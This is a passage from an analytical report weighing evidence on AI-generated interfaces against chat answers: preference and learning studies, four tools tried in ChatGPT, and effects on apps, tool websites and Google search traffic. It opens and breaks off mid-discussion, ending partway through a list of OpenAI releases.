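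The generated interface won 84% of comparisons with Claude 3.7's chat answers and lost 12%. The paper's "up to a 72% improvement" matches the difference between these two figures, so it doesn't mean the answers were 72% better. The text answers were at a disadvantage. In 26% of cases, Claude had made an artifact, and the researchers removed it and kept only the accompanying text, which may have been written to go with it.

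The interface beat GPT-4o's text by 69% to 30%. That 39-point lead is probably a better guide, although the comparison is between two different models. The lead was much larger on looks (80% to 13%) than on how efficiently users could reach their goals (54% to 41%). Both chat models are now old, and newer ones write better text as well as better pages.

Chat did best in advanced AI and machine learning, where annotators chose the interface only half the time. Chen and colleagues suggest that explanations heavy in mathematics work well as linear text. Each field had only ten queries, so one or two unusual ones could change the result considerably. Chat also did relatively well on simple how-to questions. One annotator preferred its plan for a high-school mathematics curriculum because the steps were clear. Annotators chose the interface 73% of the time for short queries, 80% for detailed ones,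 and 93.8% for data analysis, its strongest category.

### People judging answers to their own questions

The paper's most useful result comes from a smaller follow-up study. The researchers asked 76 people for five questions they would typically ask a chatbot, then showed them a generated interface and a chat answer for each. They preferred the interface in 50.8% of the 380 comparisons (193 votes) and chat in 41.1% (156 votes), with the rest tied. That lead would be barely statistically significant if all the votes were independent, and they weren't, because each person cast five.

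The lead may have shrunk because people know what they wanted when they asked their own questions, while paid annotators have to guess. The follow-up also used a different model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, for both formats, so the questions may not explain the whole difference.

People's tastes also differed. About 23 of the 76 chose the interface at least four times out of five, and about 14 strongly preferred chat. If everyone had voted independently with the same probabilities, those numbers would have been about 15 and 7. Some people apparently prefer interfaces in general and others prefer text, which is a good argument for a setting like the one ChatGPT offers for simpler visual answers.

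This study also supports letting the model choose the format. Participants preferred the generated interface 51% of the time and text 41% of the time, so an assistant that always used either one would often have given them the answer they liked less. Chen and colleagues list as a limitation that their system doesn't choose between the two.

### What a vote between two answers leaves out

A pairwise preference records which of two answers a person prefers after seeing both. It is quick to collect and captures qualities that people struggle to describe, but it doesn't show whether the preferred answer is correct.

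Suppose a household uses 200 units of electricity a month and has to choose between two tariffs. The first costs 32 cents a unit, or $64 a month. The second costs 24 cents a unit plus a fixed $30 a month, or $78 in total. If a generated page has an attractive usage slider but omits the fixed charge, it shows the second tariff at $48. A rater might well prefer this page to a correct paragraph, but a household that relied on it would overpay by $168 a year.

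Good presentation can even make the content seem better. In the study by Chen and colleagues, 86.5% of annotators' comments about credibility favoured the generated interface. One annotator called it "more professionally written", although many acknowledged that both answers were reasonable. The researchers warn that a polished, tool-like appearance may make users overconfident.

An average preference can also hide a lot of disagreement. Peng, Bigham and Wu (2026), in *Efficient Personalization of Generative User Interfaces*, had 20 people judge the same 600 pairs of generated phone screens. Any two people agreed on 62.4% of the pairs on average, when guessing would give about 50%. Researchers often express this as Krippendorff's alpha:

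α = 1 − (observed disagreement / disagreement expected by chance)

The agreement score here is 1 − 0.376/0.5, or about 0.25, where 1 would be perfect agreement. People agreed most about forms (72%) and least about screens such as logins and media players (54% to 57%). Some wanted simple screens and others wanted complete ones. Chen and colleagues found moderate agreement, 0.525 on a similar scale, when annotators compared an interface with text. So people seem to agree more about whether they want an interface than about what a good one looks like.

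Neither of the two main studies followed people over time. Participants in the follow-up were seeing this kind of interface for the first time, so some of its appeal may fade. Its appeal could also grow as people get used to it. One annotator preferred the chatbot because most people already know how to use it.

### Fewer messages, but not always less time

*When Interfaces Speak*, from the University of Hong Kong and Microsoft Research, tested whether a generated form helps people complete service tasks such as changing a flight. One agent looks up the customer's records and available options, and another model writes a form containing only the choices that are still open. After the user submits the form, the first agent makes the change. A task counts as a success only if the database ends up exactly as it should.

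*When Interfaces Speak* (2026) reports that, in a human comparison using 100 of these tasks, the forms cut the average number of dialogue rounds from 3.4 to 1.2. The researchers used only tasks for which the interface had worked in all three earlier sessions, so the reduction applies only to forms that work. Fewer rounds may not mean less time, because filling in a form with six fields counts as one round but may take as long as answering three short questions. On 85% of the tasks, most reviewers of the forms found the wait acceptable.

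The larger test included the failures and used software to simulate the user. Across nine models, the generated-interface system succeeded in at least one of three attempts 4.5 percentage points more often than a text-based system called smolagents. For Claude Opus 5, the success rates were 46.7% and 44.7%, respectively. The systems differed in other ways too, so the interface may not explain the whole difference. Of the failures, 52% involved unsuccessful use of the interface. In one case, a control accepted only one choice when the user needed to select several.

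Better interface code raised Claude Opus 5's average success rate from 31.6% to 40.3%. A small model the researchers had trained for the purpose wrote the interface, and Opus 5 did the rest of the work.

*TaskArtisan* (2026) timed people analysing data with either generated widgets or chat. Setup took 21.1 minutes with widgets and about 14 with chat, a figure inferred from the chat group's other times. The repeated steps then took 4.3 minutes with widgets and 7.8 with chat. The total times, 25.3 minutes with widgets and 21.9 with chat, were not significantly different. Participants rated their own performance much higher with the widgets.

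These times suggest that generated tools are more worthwhile when people keep them, as they can with Claude's artifacts, than when people use them for a single question. Setting up the widgets took about seven extra minutes, and each round of repeated steps saved three and a half, so a user would recover the setup time after two rounds if later rounds went equally well.

*Beyond Chat and Clicks* (2026) tested DOMSteer, which changes an existing program's interface to help the user. In a data visualisation program, people finished in about 192 seconds with DOMSteer and 260 with a chat assistant, and accuracy didn't differ significantly. But adapting a program that people have already built is easier than generating a new one.

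Text can be faster too. In *Neither Replacement nor Panacea* (2026), people made industrial decisions using either a chatbot or a graphical dashboard. The study found no overall difference in accuracy. The chatbot was faster on the easier task but lost this advantage as the tasks became more complex. A companion study, *Comparing LLM-Based Conversational and Graphical Interfaces for Industrial Decision Tasks* (2026), found the chatbot significantly faster in two of four tasks. Participants also said it took less effort, though the measurements showed this less consistently. The dashboards appear to have been conventional rather than generated, so these studies compare chat with graphical interfaces in general. They still fit the other results reasonably well, since text did best when the question was simple.

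### Whether people learn more

The best evidence of a learning benefit comes from Google. In *An Experimental Evaluation of an AI-Powered Interactive Learning Platform*, Heldreth, Akrong and colleagues (2025) randomly assigned 60 American high-school students to study a chapter on brain development, half as a PDF and half in Learn Your Way, an experimental system that turns a chapter into interactive text with quizzes, slides, audio lessons and other formats. On an immediate test, the Learn Your Way group scored 9.2 out of 12 and the PDF group scored 8.2. Three to seven days later, the scores were 4.7 and 4.0 out of 6.

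This is encouraging, but it doesn't show that interfaces teach better than text answers, because no student used a chatbot. Everyone in the Learn Your Way group also took quizzes as they studied, and testing oneself helps memory in almost any format. That group studied for longer too, about 31 minutes on average compared with 22 for the PDF group. The researchers found no significant effect of study time, but with 30 students in each group they could easily have missed one.

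The results are also statistically significant only on a one-sided test, which checks only for an advantage in the direction the researchers predicted. Each result had a p-value of about 0.03. A two-sided test would give about 0.06, just above the usual threshold of 0.05. *Towards an AI-Augmented Textbook* (2025) appears to report the same trial, so it isn't independent confirmation.

A much smaller study, *From Passive Consumption to Active Interaction* (2026), made a closer comparison with chat. Eight people studied mathematical proofs with an interactive explanation and with an ordinary chatbot. They clearly preferred the interactive version, but their quiz scores averaged 80% with it and 77.5% with the chatbot. Eight people are too few to rule out a real learning benefit, but the study shows that people can clearly prefer an interface without scoring much higher with it.

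Ratings of how well something supports understanding have the same problem. Learners in *Auto-Slides* (2025) rated generated slides above chat for clarity and support for understanding, but these were opinions, not test scores. In *Ultra Strong Machine Learning* (2025), AI judges gave high marks to long, well-structured explanations that helped learners no more than studying alone. Brief explanations by experts did help learners who had started out strong. These findings are exploratory and concern written explanations. But the long explanations probably didn't help because an explanation can be more complicated than the task itself, and that would apply equally to a page with a dozen features.

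Learning studies may also use material with fewer errors than people get in practice. For *Generative Lecture*, a system that adds interactive examples to lecture videos, Jo and colleagues (2025) had experts check the examples in advance, because diagrams generated on the spot can be unreliable, and corrected minor errors by hand before the study. That was sensible for testing the design, but a student who asks for a simulation at home gets one that nobody has checked.

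### Eight weeks with three versions of one assistant

Most of these comparisons come from people testing systems they built. Google studied its own generated pages and Learn Your Way, and Chen and colleagues tested their own design. They published enough detail for others to find weaknesses in the studies, and Google released the freelancers' pages for future comparisons. But builders choose the prompts, the rivals and the measures, and removing Claude's artifacts shows how much these choices might matter. OpenAI's launch material for Intelligent UI includes no comparable results.

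An independent trial could randomly assign people to one of three versions of the same assistant for eight weeks. One would answer only in text, one would always generate an interface, and one would choose between the two. Participants would ask their own questions and experience real waiting times. Each week they would also do a task with a known answer, such as picking the cheaper electricity tariff for their household. Researchers would record whether they chose correctly and how long they took from typing the question to making the decision.

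If 70% of the text group chose correctly, a study would need about 1,250 people in each group to have an 80% chance of detecting a rise to 75% at the usual 5% significance level. Recruiting that many is difficult for a university but easy for a company with hundreds of millions of users. People using the assistant to study would take a test a month later without the assistant's help. Asking everyone in the first week and again in the eighth which format they preferred would show how much of the initial enthusiasm was novelty.

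The text answers would have to be good, with tables and clear formatting, because raters already much prefer these to plain paragraphs. Comparing the second and third groups would then show whether the model can identify when an interface is worth the wait.

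## Whether generated tools replace apps and websites

If people like generated tools enough to wait for them, they may stop opening the apps and websites that do the same jobs. This is already plausible for small tools that people need once, such as a bill splitter, but much less so for apps that keep a person's records. Among websites, pages built around a public formula are most at risk of losing visitors, although nobody has yet measured how many visits they lose to generated tools.

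### The case against the small app

The argument about apps drew particular attention in China. Six days after OpenAI released Intelligent UI, the technology column AI价值官 (2026) pointed out in *模型长出交互界面，“手搓”AI应用要全面退潮了？* that phone users have spent twenty years finding an app and then following the steps its designers set. With Intelligent UI, they describe what they need and the model makes the tool.

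The column gives the example of a weekend trip, for which a traveller might once have used one app for the route, a calculator to share the costs and a notes app for the packing list. ChatGPT could put all three on one card and adjust the budget when another friend joins. AI价值官 expects calculators, to-do lists, body mass index (BMI) tools and trip planners to be worst affected, because each does one job and people open it only when they need it. 9to5Google's *Gemini’s generative UIs are the future of ‘there’s an app for that’* (2025) had already predicted that Google's version of the technology would lead to a new generation of apps.

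Whether a generated tool saves time over an app depends on how often a person needs it. As a rough example, if an app takes 60 seconds to find and install and 5 seconds to open each time, and a generated tool takes 20 seconds to request and receive each time, then after three uses the app has taken 75 seconds and the generated tools 60. The totals are equal after four uses, and after ten they are 110 seconds for the app and 200 for the generated tools. The argument for generated tools is therefore strong for a tool that somebody needs twice a year and weak for one they use every morning.

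That changes if people can reopen a generated tool as quickly as an app. The first use would still take 20 seconds, but each later use would take 5, so the generated tool would save a total of 45 seconds compared with the app, however often they used it.

### Four tools on trial

Pathak (2026), in *I made 4 apps with ChatGPT's Intelligent UI*, tested the idea for the technology site Android Authority. ChatGPT made a working bill splitter in a couple of seconds, with options to add a tip, choose the number of people paying and split the bill unevenly. Pathak wondered who needed it, since Apple's Siri can already work out one person's share from a photo of the bill. But he thought it a reasonable alternative to apps full of advertisements.

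The trip planner was more useful. Pathak asked for three days in Goa with a focus on food and got three tabs, each with a timetable, suggested dishes and checkboxes. ChatGPT also asked which areas and activities Pathak preferred, then revised the itinerary and offered a budget for two people. The request was similar to AI价值官's weekend trip, so the result supports that example fairly well.

A tool for following Formula 1 motor racing did worse. It showed the next race and some news, but only the top three drivers in the standings. Pathak had to go to the sport's official website for the full standings and schedule. According to a note at the bottom, the tool didn't update itself, so a fan would have to run the prompt again the following week.

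The coffee tool was the most ambitious, but it failed at its main job. It had settings for different coffees, recipe steps and a journal for tasting notes. The timer didn't work, even after ChatGPT rebuilt the whole tool, and the journal kept entries only for the current session. Pathak liked the visual recipe and would ask for another, but preferred a dedicated app for notes.

Pathak concluded that "Interactive Answers" would be a more realistic name for the feature. Other writers more readily call the results apps. In *Forget downloading apps*, TechRadar's reviewer made six of them with ChatGPT and was surprised by the results, and Koumpouras (2026), in *Το δωρεάν εργαλείο του ChatGPT δημιουργεί εφαρμογές στη στιγμή για όλους*, told Greek readers that the free tool creates apps on the spot. Komando (2026), in *Make ChatGPT build you a calculator instead of giving you a lecture*, recommends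 the feature for making calculators, a narrower use that fits Pathak's experience better because a calculator doesn't need to store information or retrieve news.

Four tools are too few to give a failure rate, and Pathak tried them within weeks of the launch. The trial is more useful for showing the different kinds of failure.

### What a better model could fix

| Problem in Pathak's trial | Would a better model fix it? | What the product would need |
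|---|---|---|
| Only three drivers in the standings | Probably | Nothing new |
| A timer that doesn't run | Probably, if the cause is faulty code | Perhaps a tested timer component |
| Standings that go out of date | No | A data source the tool can check by itself |
| Journal entries that disappear | No | Storage linked to the user's account |
| No single place to find saved tools | No | A list of them in ChatGPT |

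The timer is the hardest to classify. If random coding slips broke one timer in ten, two in a row would fail only about once in a hundred attempts. A lasting cause is more likely, such as a missing component or a mistake that the model copied from the first version into the second. If a component is missing, a better model won't fix the timer until OpenAI adds that component.

Improving the model will not let the journal save a note about last Tuesday's coffee, because the model finishes its work before the user writes the note. Claude's artifacts and ChatGPT's own flashcard library show that these limits are design choices. OpenAI could probably add storage for its generated tools and a list of them within months if it wanted to.

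OpenAI would then take on more of an app developer's work. Someone with two years of coffee notes needs backups, a way to export the notes and some assurance that next year's ChatGPT will still open them. Once OpenAI provides these, the coffee journal is an app that OpenAI hosts. That may suit the coffee drinker, but the developer of a coffee app has still lost a customer.

Installed apps would keep some advantages. A phone's own timer rings when the screen is locked, which matters more for long timers, and a downloaded bill splitter works in a restaurant with no signal. A tool generated inside a chat would need help from the phone's operating system to ring on a locked phone, and some way of working offline to split a bill without a signal.

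### Companies that sell little besides an interface

Many young AI companies sell subscriptions to another company's model with a fixed screen and some prepared instructions added. *聊天框的终结，OpenAI向12亿用户下放GPT-6* (2026), from the Chinese business site Huxiu, warns that models which make their own screens will absorb what these companies sell. Dai Kun, an analyst at the research firm Forrester, told Huxiu that Intelligent UI would squeeze many of these companies, along with simple online business software.

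Huxiu's main example is Jasper, a company once worth $1.5 billion that sold templates for writing marketing copy. Its valuation fell and its staff faced layoffs as ChatGPT improved and OpenAI let users make customised versions of the chatbot. Jasper shows that a general assistant can take over the work of a specialised product. But its troubles came from ChatGPT's better writing and easier customisation, so they are weak evidence about generated interfaces. Julius AI and ChartAI, which make charts from people's data, are closer tests because ChatGPT now draws charts in its replies.

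Both analysts Huxiu interviewed expect much business software to survive. A payroll system holds a company's records, controls who may see each salary and has to follow tax law. A generated form could replace the screen where a manager enters hours, but not the system behind it. Yan Bin of the research firm Gartner also advises companies to treat generated interfaces as reference tools for now and not to base key decisions on them.

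Yan also says that ordinary users will be able to get custom software that was previously too expensive to make, which weakens the claim that generated tools will replace apps. If a football coach asks for a tool that rotates fourteen children through seven positions, no developer loses a sale, because no such tool was on sale. Counting generated tools would therefore greatly overstate the number of apps they replace.

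AI价值官 extends the argument to platforms that let people without programming skills build their own apps. Ant Group, ByteDance, Baidu and Tencent all backed such products in late 2025 and early 2026. The column suggests that these platforms may be a detour, because people who can get a tool by asking a question have no reason to build an app first.

As evidence, the AI价值官 column notes that the platforms are already changing direction. Ant moved the head of its product, Lingguang, to another job in June and has been turning Lingguang into a personal assistant. Tencent's Tusi shifted in August towards helping developers with registration and compliance paperwork. AI价值官 thinks the companies anticipated native interfaces. Weak demand is a simpler explanation, at least for Tusi, which the column says never caught on beyond developers.

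Small tools also do well where nobody asks for them. In a limited trial, the video site Bilibili let creators publish games and tools alongside their videos, and people used them more than 8.5 million times. AI价值官 expects assistants to take some of this traffic, since a traveller can ask for an itinerary directly instead of finding one under a travel post. That may be right for itineraries, but an assistant that waits for a request doesn't compete with a game that people play only because they saw it below a video.

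### A calculator above the links

A generated tool's effect on websites depends heavily on where it appears. Somebody who types "mortgage calculator" into Google is looking for a website, so if they use a calculator in the AI Overview instead, some site has probably lost a visit. When somebody asks ChatGPT whether they can afford a house, they are already in a conversation, and the calculator may replace only a paragraph of text.

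AI Overviews, which appear on Google's results page, have more than 2.5 billion monthly users, according to Search Engine Journal's *Google’s Generated Interfaces Could Compete With Tool Pages*.

ChatGPT can still reduce visits to websites, but the loss is harder to see. A person who gets used to asking ChatGPT may skip the Google search. The number of searches then falls, but the website's share of clicks stays the same.

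Search Engine Journal expects pages that apply public formulas to ordinary inputs to be the easiest to reproduce. A BMI calculator, for example, divides weight in kilograms by the square of height in metres, so any competent model can write one. Tools that depend on private data or require a login, such as a property site's estimate of a house's value from its own sales records, are harder to reproduce.

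Educational sites face the earliest competition because Google started with study aids and quizzes. Software companies may also lose a form of advertising, since many offer a free file converter or website checker to help people discover their paid products. If people use Google's converter instead, they won't discover the company through its tool. *Which Tool Pages Are Most At Risk From AI Overviews?* (Pilkington, 2026) gives a similar warning to small businesses whose calculators and checkers bring in visitors from Google.

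These pages may lose visitors even if they are better than generated tools. Google's raters preferred pages by freelance experts to generated ones, so a carefully made calculator could well be better than a generated one. But a searcher who already has a working calculator on the screen has little reason to click a link to check whether another is better.

Having data does not always help a site, either. A site that compares electricity tariffs does only trivial arithmetic, and is valuable because it keeps its list of prices current. But if those prices are on a public page, Google can read them and use them in its own comparison.

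### Google as everyone's Booking.com

In *Generative UI in Search Ends the Page-as-Destination Era* (May 2026), the web consultant Slobodan Manic argued that websites used to attract visitors and persuade them with their own design and wording, but Google now puts the sites' data into its own layout, with its own typography and choice of button. In Manic's account, people no longer visit the site, so its owner loses the usual measures of success, such as page views and the share of visitors who buy something. Site owners would instead have to ask whether Google used their data and whether the button leads back to them.

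In October, Manic compared this with the hotel trade in Search Engine Journal's *Generative UI Could Turn Google Into Your Booking.com* (2026). Booking.com controls the page where travellers compare hotels it doesn't own, and the hotels pay a commission for the guests it sends. At a 15% commission, a hotel keeps $170 from a $200 room. It also has to compete with rivals that are one tap away on the same page.

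Hotels have found this position hard to escape. O'Neill (2026), in *Hotels Spent $100 Million Fighting OTAs. Did It Actually Work?*, reviews a decade of attempts by hotels, including Hilton's "Stop Clicking Around" campaign, to persuade travellers to book directly rather than through online travel agencies (OTAs) such as Booking.com and Expedia.

Google has since built something very close to Manic's picture for hotel bookings. In August, *3 new ways to plan and book travel in Search* announced that Americans could book a room without leaving AI Mode. The user selects "Continue on Google", chooses a room, checks the cancellation terms and pays with Google Pay. The partners include Hilton and Marriott, but also Expedia and Booking.com, which now supplies rooms to Google's page. The hotel or travel site remains the official seller and handles customer service.

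The comparison holds for businesses that have something Google needs. Google can't generate a vacant hotel room in Lisbon, so it has to deal with a company that has one. The comparison is probably too optimistic for calculator pages. A hotel that pays a 15% commission still gets a guest and most of the money, but a site whose calculator Google can rebuild from a public formula gets no visitor and no payment.

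Manic also overstates the case in places. Google's generated layouts can probably draw on ordinary prose, as AI Overviews already do, yet Manic calls schema markup, labels that help software read a page, the only way for a site's data to appear in them. And people will still want to visit many sites, if only to read a long article or check a hotel's own photographs before paying.

Hotels are handling ChatGPT more cautiously. Radisson and Motel 6 launched apps in ChatGPT a day apart in July. Both apps help people find a room but send them elsewhere to pay (Constantin, 2026, *Hotels are moving into ChatGPT, but not the payment*), so the hotels keep control of the final step and the customer's details. This may not be entirely the hotels' choice, since OpenAI generally approves purchases through plugins only for physical goods. Customers don't seem to mind, as Constantin cites research by the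 consulting firm Accenture in which only 9% of people wanted AI to buy things for them.

### How many clicks AI Overviews take

The available studies measure AI Overviews in general, and most appeared before Google began adding generated tools in August. They show what happened when written answers moved onto the results page, the closest precedent for generated tools.

The Pew Research Center found that 8% of search visits with an AI summary led to a click on an ordinary result, compared with 15% of those without one. Ahrefs, which sells software for analysing search traffic, examined 300,000 keywords. In February 2026, according to PPC Land's *Google adds 5 outbound link features to AI Mode and AI Overviews*, it found that the click rate for top-ranking pages was 58% lower when an AI Overview appeared, compared with 34.5% lower in April 2025.

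These comparisons may exaggerate the effect, because searches that produce AI summaries differ from those that don't. Xu, Iqbal and Montgomery (2026), in *Measuring Google AI Overviews*, ran 55,393 trending searches over 40 days in March and April. They got an AI Overview for 64.7% of the searches phrased as questions and 9.5% of the others. Someone who asks how tall an actor is may not need to leave the results page even without an AI summary, while someone who types the name of a shop probably wants to visit its website.

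A randomised experiment avoids this problem, because chance decides who sees the summaries. Xu and colleagues cite one by Agarwal and Sen, in which AI Overviews reduced clicks on unpaid results by 38% and increased searches that ended without a click by 33%. Users who saw the summaries didn't report being more satisfied. The 38% is probably the best single estimate of how much written summaries reduce clicks on unpaid results.

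The effect on a particular site can be smaller. *Impact of AI Search Summaries on Website Traffic* (2026), by Khosravi and Yoganarasimhan, studied English Wikipedia using comparison groups instead of random assignment. Xu and colleagues report its estimate as a loss of about 15% of traffic. If that lasted a year, Wikipedia would receive about 1.2 billion fewer visits directly from search engines. The full loss could be larger, because this figure excludes the further articles those visitors would have opened.

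Publishers' own reports vary even more. A survey by Digital Content Next, a trade group, found that the typical publisher got 10% fewer visits from Google Search over eight weeks in mid-2025 than a year earlier. The music site Stereogum blamed AI Overviews for the loss of 70% of its advertising revenue, and the travel blog The Planet D closed after its traffic fell by 90%. But a site's traffic can also collapse for other reasons, such as a change in how Google ranks sites.

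Websites that lose visits usually lose income too. Xu and colleagues found advertisements on at least 50.6% of the pages that AI Overviews cited, and Google's own advertisements continued to appear on the results page. A calculator page that earns $20 for every 1,000 visits would lose $760 a month if its 100,000 monthly visits fell by 38%.

None of these studies measures generated tools separately, so the 38% figure is only a guess for a calculator page. It could be higher, because someone who has finished a calculation needs nothing more from the web, whereas a summary can make a reader want the full article. It could be lower if Google rarely shows generated tools or people distrust them. Google hasn't published how often they appear.

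Site owners can't find out from Google's own statistics either. Search Engine Journal notes that a new report in Search Console, Google's service for site owners, shows how often a page appears in AI Overviews and AI Mode. It doesn't count clicks or separate generated interfaces from ordinary summaries.

One site tried to get around the missing click data by opting out of Google's AI features. *Google's AI Features Sent One Site An Estimated 21% Of Its Clicks* (Southern, 2026) also reports a possible rise in clicks on the site's regular listings after it opted out. Those clicks would have to rise by about 27% to make up for the lost ones, because out of every 1,000 clicks, about 210 had come through AI features and 790 through regular listings. AI answers therefore send some visitors to sites as well as keeping others on Google. But Google presumably went on answering the same questions from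 other sites' pages, so the test can't show how many clicks the site would get if AI Overviews didn't exist.

Website owners who publish both calculators and articles could roughly estimate the effect of generated tools by comparing traffic to the two. Suppose visits from Google to the articles fall by 10% between July and October, while visits to the calculators fall by 20%. Written summaries affect both, so the extra fall might come from generated tools. It could also be seasonal, since fewer people may look at mortgages in autumn. To check, the owner would need to compare the same months in earlier years.

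### Google adds more links

Google maintains that AI will add to the web, not replace it. Reid, its head of search, said in November that "people don't want purely AI, they want AI and the web" (Schwartz, 2026, *Google Says Users Don't Just Want AI*). Reid also distinguished between websites that AI can easily replace, which would probably include unit converters, and those that it can't.

Google has changed the links in its AI search features twice this year. In May, it announced updates to help people find relevant websites and original content from AI Mode and AI Overviews (Budaraju, 2026, *5 new ways to explore the web with generative AI in Search*). In June, *Google looks to ease publisher concerns over the impact of AI Overviews* (Hutchinson, 2026) described further efforts to reassure publishers about lost traffic. On October 15, Google promised clearer links in both features and more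 context about sources (Budaraju, 2026, *More ways to connect with the web from Search*).

Better links should help sites that people want to read. Someone who reads a summary of a medical study may well click through to the study or to a doctor's explanation of it. Links are less useful to a site whose tool Google has rebuilt. A borrower who has just found out that a loan costs $1,799 a month already has the answer, and because nobody owns the formula, Google has no obvious source to credit.

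The law may limit Google more than its own promises do, at least in Europe. In July, the European Commission fined Google €460 million for favouring its own services in travel and shopping searches, as Ars Technica's *Google complies with EU rules for travel searches* (2026) reports. Google then changed its European results but complained that they had become much worse. Xu and colleagues note that the Commission and Britain's competition authority are also examining AI Overviews. For now, a European site that compares hotel prices has some protection from Google's own version, but it isn't clear that a site with a loan calculator has any.

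## Whether chat remains the main way of using AI

Generated tools may displace chat as well as apps and websites. A borrower can drag a slider instead of sending a message, and some people, including a few at OpenAI, think chat will fall out of use.

"Chat" covers two things that ChatGPT happened to combine. Chat as input is asking for what you want in your own words, typed or spoken. Chat as output is getting the reply as text in a conversation. Someone who types a question and gets a calculator has used chat only as input. Someone who presses a "Summarise" button in an email program gets text back without typing a request.

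OpenAI, Google and Anthropic have mostly changed the output. People still begin by typing or speaking, so the input that generated interfaces replace is mainly follow-up messages. People who predict the end of chat often mean different parts of it, either the messages users send or the responses they get, which explains much of the disagreement about its future.

### Asking in words and getting an interface back

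In December 2025, ten months before Intelligent UI, Simo wrote that ChatGPT was moving "toward a fully generative UI that brings in the right components". People choosing a restaurant want photos and details side by side, and people converting a measurement want a result they can read at a glance. Both groups still ask in words, and only the form of the answer changes.

The case for keeping words as the input is that people can use them to express wishes nobody anticipated. A trip-planning form needs a field for every preference a traveller might have, and most travellers leave most of the fields blank. A sentence such as "three days in Goa, mostly for the food, and my father can't manage stairs" covers only what matters to that family.

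Simo's essay also describes a way to ask follow-up questions without typing them. Readers would be able to tap a highlighted name, such as "Habsburgs" in an answer about the Thirty Years' War, or select any phrase, and get an explanation without losing their place.

OpenAI's experience with its writing tool, canvas, supports keeping people in the chat. Simo says people liked canvas but it interrupted their flow, so OpenAI was moving editing back into the chat. But OpenAI gave image-making its own area, so even in Simo's vision of the future, people do some tasks outside the chat.

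### The trouble with a blank box

In *Post-Chat UI*, Pike (2025) compares chat to the terminal, the text-only screen that people used before computers had windows and icons. Both are powerful and flexible, but a blank input field is daunting, and text is a bad way to select and move things. Pike would keep chat as a fallback and use more suitable controls for most tasks.

The design firm thirteen23 goes further in *The prompt-box paradox*. It describes an interface that would form around a person's goal, such as understanding how a business is doing, offer new controls as the person learned more, and disappear when the work was done.

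Chinese technology writers have put the prediction most bluntly. In *聊天已死* ("Chat is dead"), TMTPost asked in June 2026 whether the era of the dialogue box was over, and Huxiu titled its October article on Intelligent UI "the end of the chat box". Below that title, Huxiu says more mildly that chatbots haven't disappeared and that the box is changing from an answer window into an interface generator. That is nearly Simo's position, since people would still type into the box.

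Some evidence suggests that a blank text box keeps people from seeing what AI can do. OpenAI's *AI for human agency* reports that the typical power user uses seven times as much computing power as the typical user and applies advanced functions to a wider range of tasks. Someone who has never thought to ask for a savings calculator might use one if it appeared without being requested. But the gap may also exist because most people have simpler needs, which a better interface wouldn't change.

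People do learn what to type into the chat box to some extent. OpenAI's *How ChatGPT adoption has expanded* (2026) found in June, before Intelligent UI existed, that people's use of ChatGPT tends to grow with time, both in how often they turn to it and in how many kinds of task they give it. The finding would overstate how much people learn if those who never worked out what to type had given up and dropped out of the later figures.

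Predictions of chat's replacement are also older than ChatGPT. In a talk at AI Engineer's 2025 World's Fair, a speaker named Piras traced the debate to a May 2022 post by Linus Lee, which questioned whether raw text completion was the right long-term interface. Piras calls the situation "Schrödinger's Chat", because designers who can list chat's faults keep using it every day. ChatGPT has since reached 1.2 billion weekly users, according to Huxiu. This popularity shows that people will put up with chat to use a good model, but they might not choose it if the same model came with a better interface, an option few of them had until recently.

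Some people would resist the change. Huxiu reports that software engineers on the forum Hacker News worry that too many visuals and forms will slow the exchange of dense information. For example, an engineer can easily paste a 200-line error log into a blank text box.

### Remembering where the button is

Supporters of fixed interfaces argue that people get fast at software through habit, because the controls stay in the same place, and that an interface a model makes afresh each time removes this consistency.

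A rough calculation gives the size of the effect. Someone who doesn't know a screen has to scan it, and on average looks at half the controls before finding the right one. For someone who knows the screen, the time grows much more slowly with the number of controls, roughly following a rule called Hick's law:

unfamiliar screen: T = s × (n + 1) / 2

familiar screen: T = a + b × log₂(n + 1)

Here n is the number of controls and s is the time to look at one. The constants a and b vary with the person and the task. With 24 controls, s = 0.25 seconds, a = 0.2 and b = 0.15, finding a control takes 3.1 seconds on the unfamiliar screen and 0.9 on the familiar one. If the screen kept changing, a clerk who does this 200 times a day would lose about seven minutes a day, while a borrower who uses a loan calculator once would lose about two seconds.

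Microsoft tried a mild form of changing interface in Office 2000, whose menus hid commands that a person hadn't used lately, so a menu could look different from one week to the next. Microsoft dropped the idea when it redesigned Office in 2007.

Conffab's *Generative UI and the Ephemeral Interface* is a designer's response to Gemini 3's generated pages. The designer had been sceptical for much the same reason, after imagining a design program that rearranged itself to suit each task. The objection hardly applies to a newly generated page about Van Gogh, because nobody has habits to lose there.

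Dodds reports in *AI beyond the chat interface* that the usability researcher Jakob Nielsen considers AI the third great change in user interfaces, because people now specify the result they want instead of the steps. Nielsen lists serious problems with chat and doubts that early tools such as ChatGPT and Bard represent what will follow. His objections are to chat, and a generated interface with visible controls might address them as well as a fixed one.

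OpenAI's own product provides the better evidence for fixed interfaces. In the weeks around the launch of Intelligent UI, OpenAI expanded Finances, where people connect their bank accounts, and added summaries to a Health tab. It also gave shoppers folders for saved products and gave some paying users Space, where they keep pages and files. These are all permanent places that people can learn to find. OpenAI seems to generate interfaces for single questions and build fixed ones for things people come back to.

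thirteen23 has a reply, which is that the system could remember a person's goals from one session to the next and reshape itself to fit. But remembering that somebody is saving for a car is different from keeping the "Add deposit" button in the same corner. The usability argument is really against regenerating a layout. A generated tool that stays put, like a saved Claude artifact, escapes most of it.

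### An agent that sends text messages

In 2025, OpenAI's Sam Altman told reporters that models had "already saturated the chat use case", according to Futurism. The Decoder reported in *OpenAI CEO Sam Altman shifts focus to GPT-6* that OpenAI was betting on agents that carry out complex tasks over long periods. Interface design matters much less if people only hand over a task and collect the result.

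In June 2026 an unnamed senior employee at OpenAI told the Financial Times that "chat is dead". Thibault Sottiaux, who leads OpenAI's core product and platform teams, described the plan behind the remark as one personal agent that people could reach from a phone, a computer or the web, or talk to in the car (Wheatley, 2026, *OpenAI's planned 'superapp' gets closer as one employee says 'chat is dead'*). OpenAI's *From Capability to Utility* calls voice "the next form factor" because people could use it without stopping what they are doing to open an app and type.

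These statements concern the output more than the input. *Wait, Chat Is Dead?* (Battelle, 2026) quotes another OpenAI executive from the same report, who expected "a single entity that I can talk to", which would still use chat as input. Battelle objects on commercial grounds, because chat brought OpenAI its billion users and the company had been promoting its plans for a huge advertising business only two months earlier. Wheatley thinks the new app is mainly about packaging and revenue, and is meant to lead free users to paid products. An employee's remark to a newspaper at such a time is partly a sales pitch, so it deserves less weight than what OpenAI released afterwards.

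The releases came close together:

- **September 23:** Voice arrived in ChatGPT Work, so people could ask aloud for documents and spreadsheets.
- **September 29:** OpenAI introduced dots, always-on agents that keep working between conversations on their own cloud computer.
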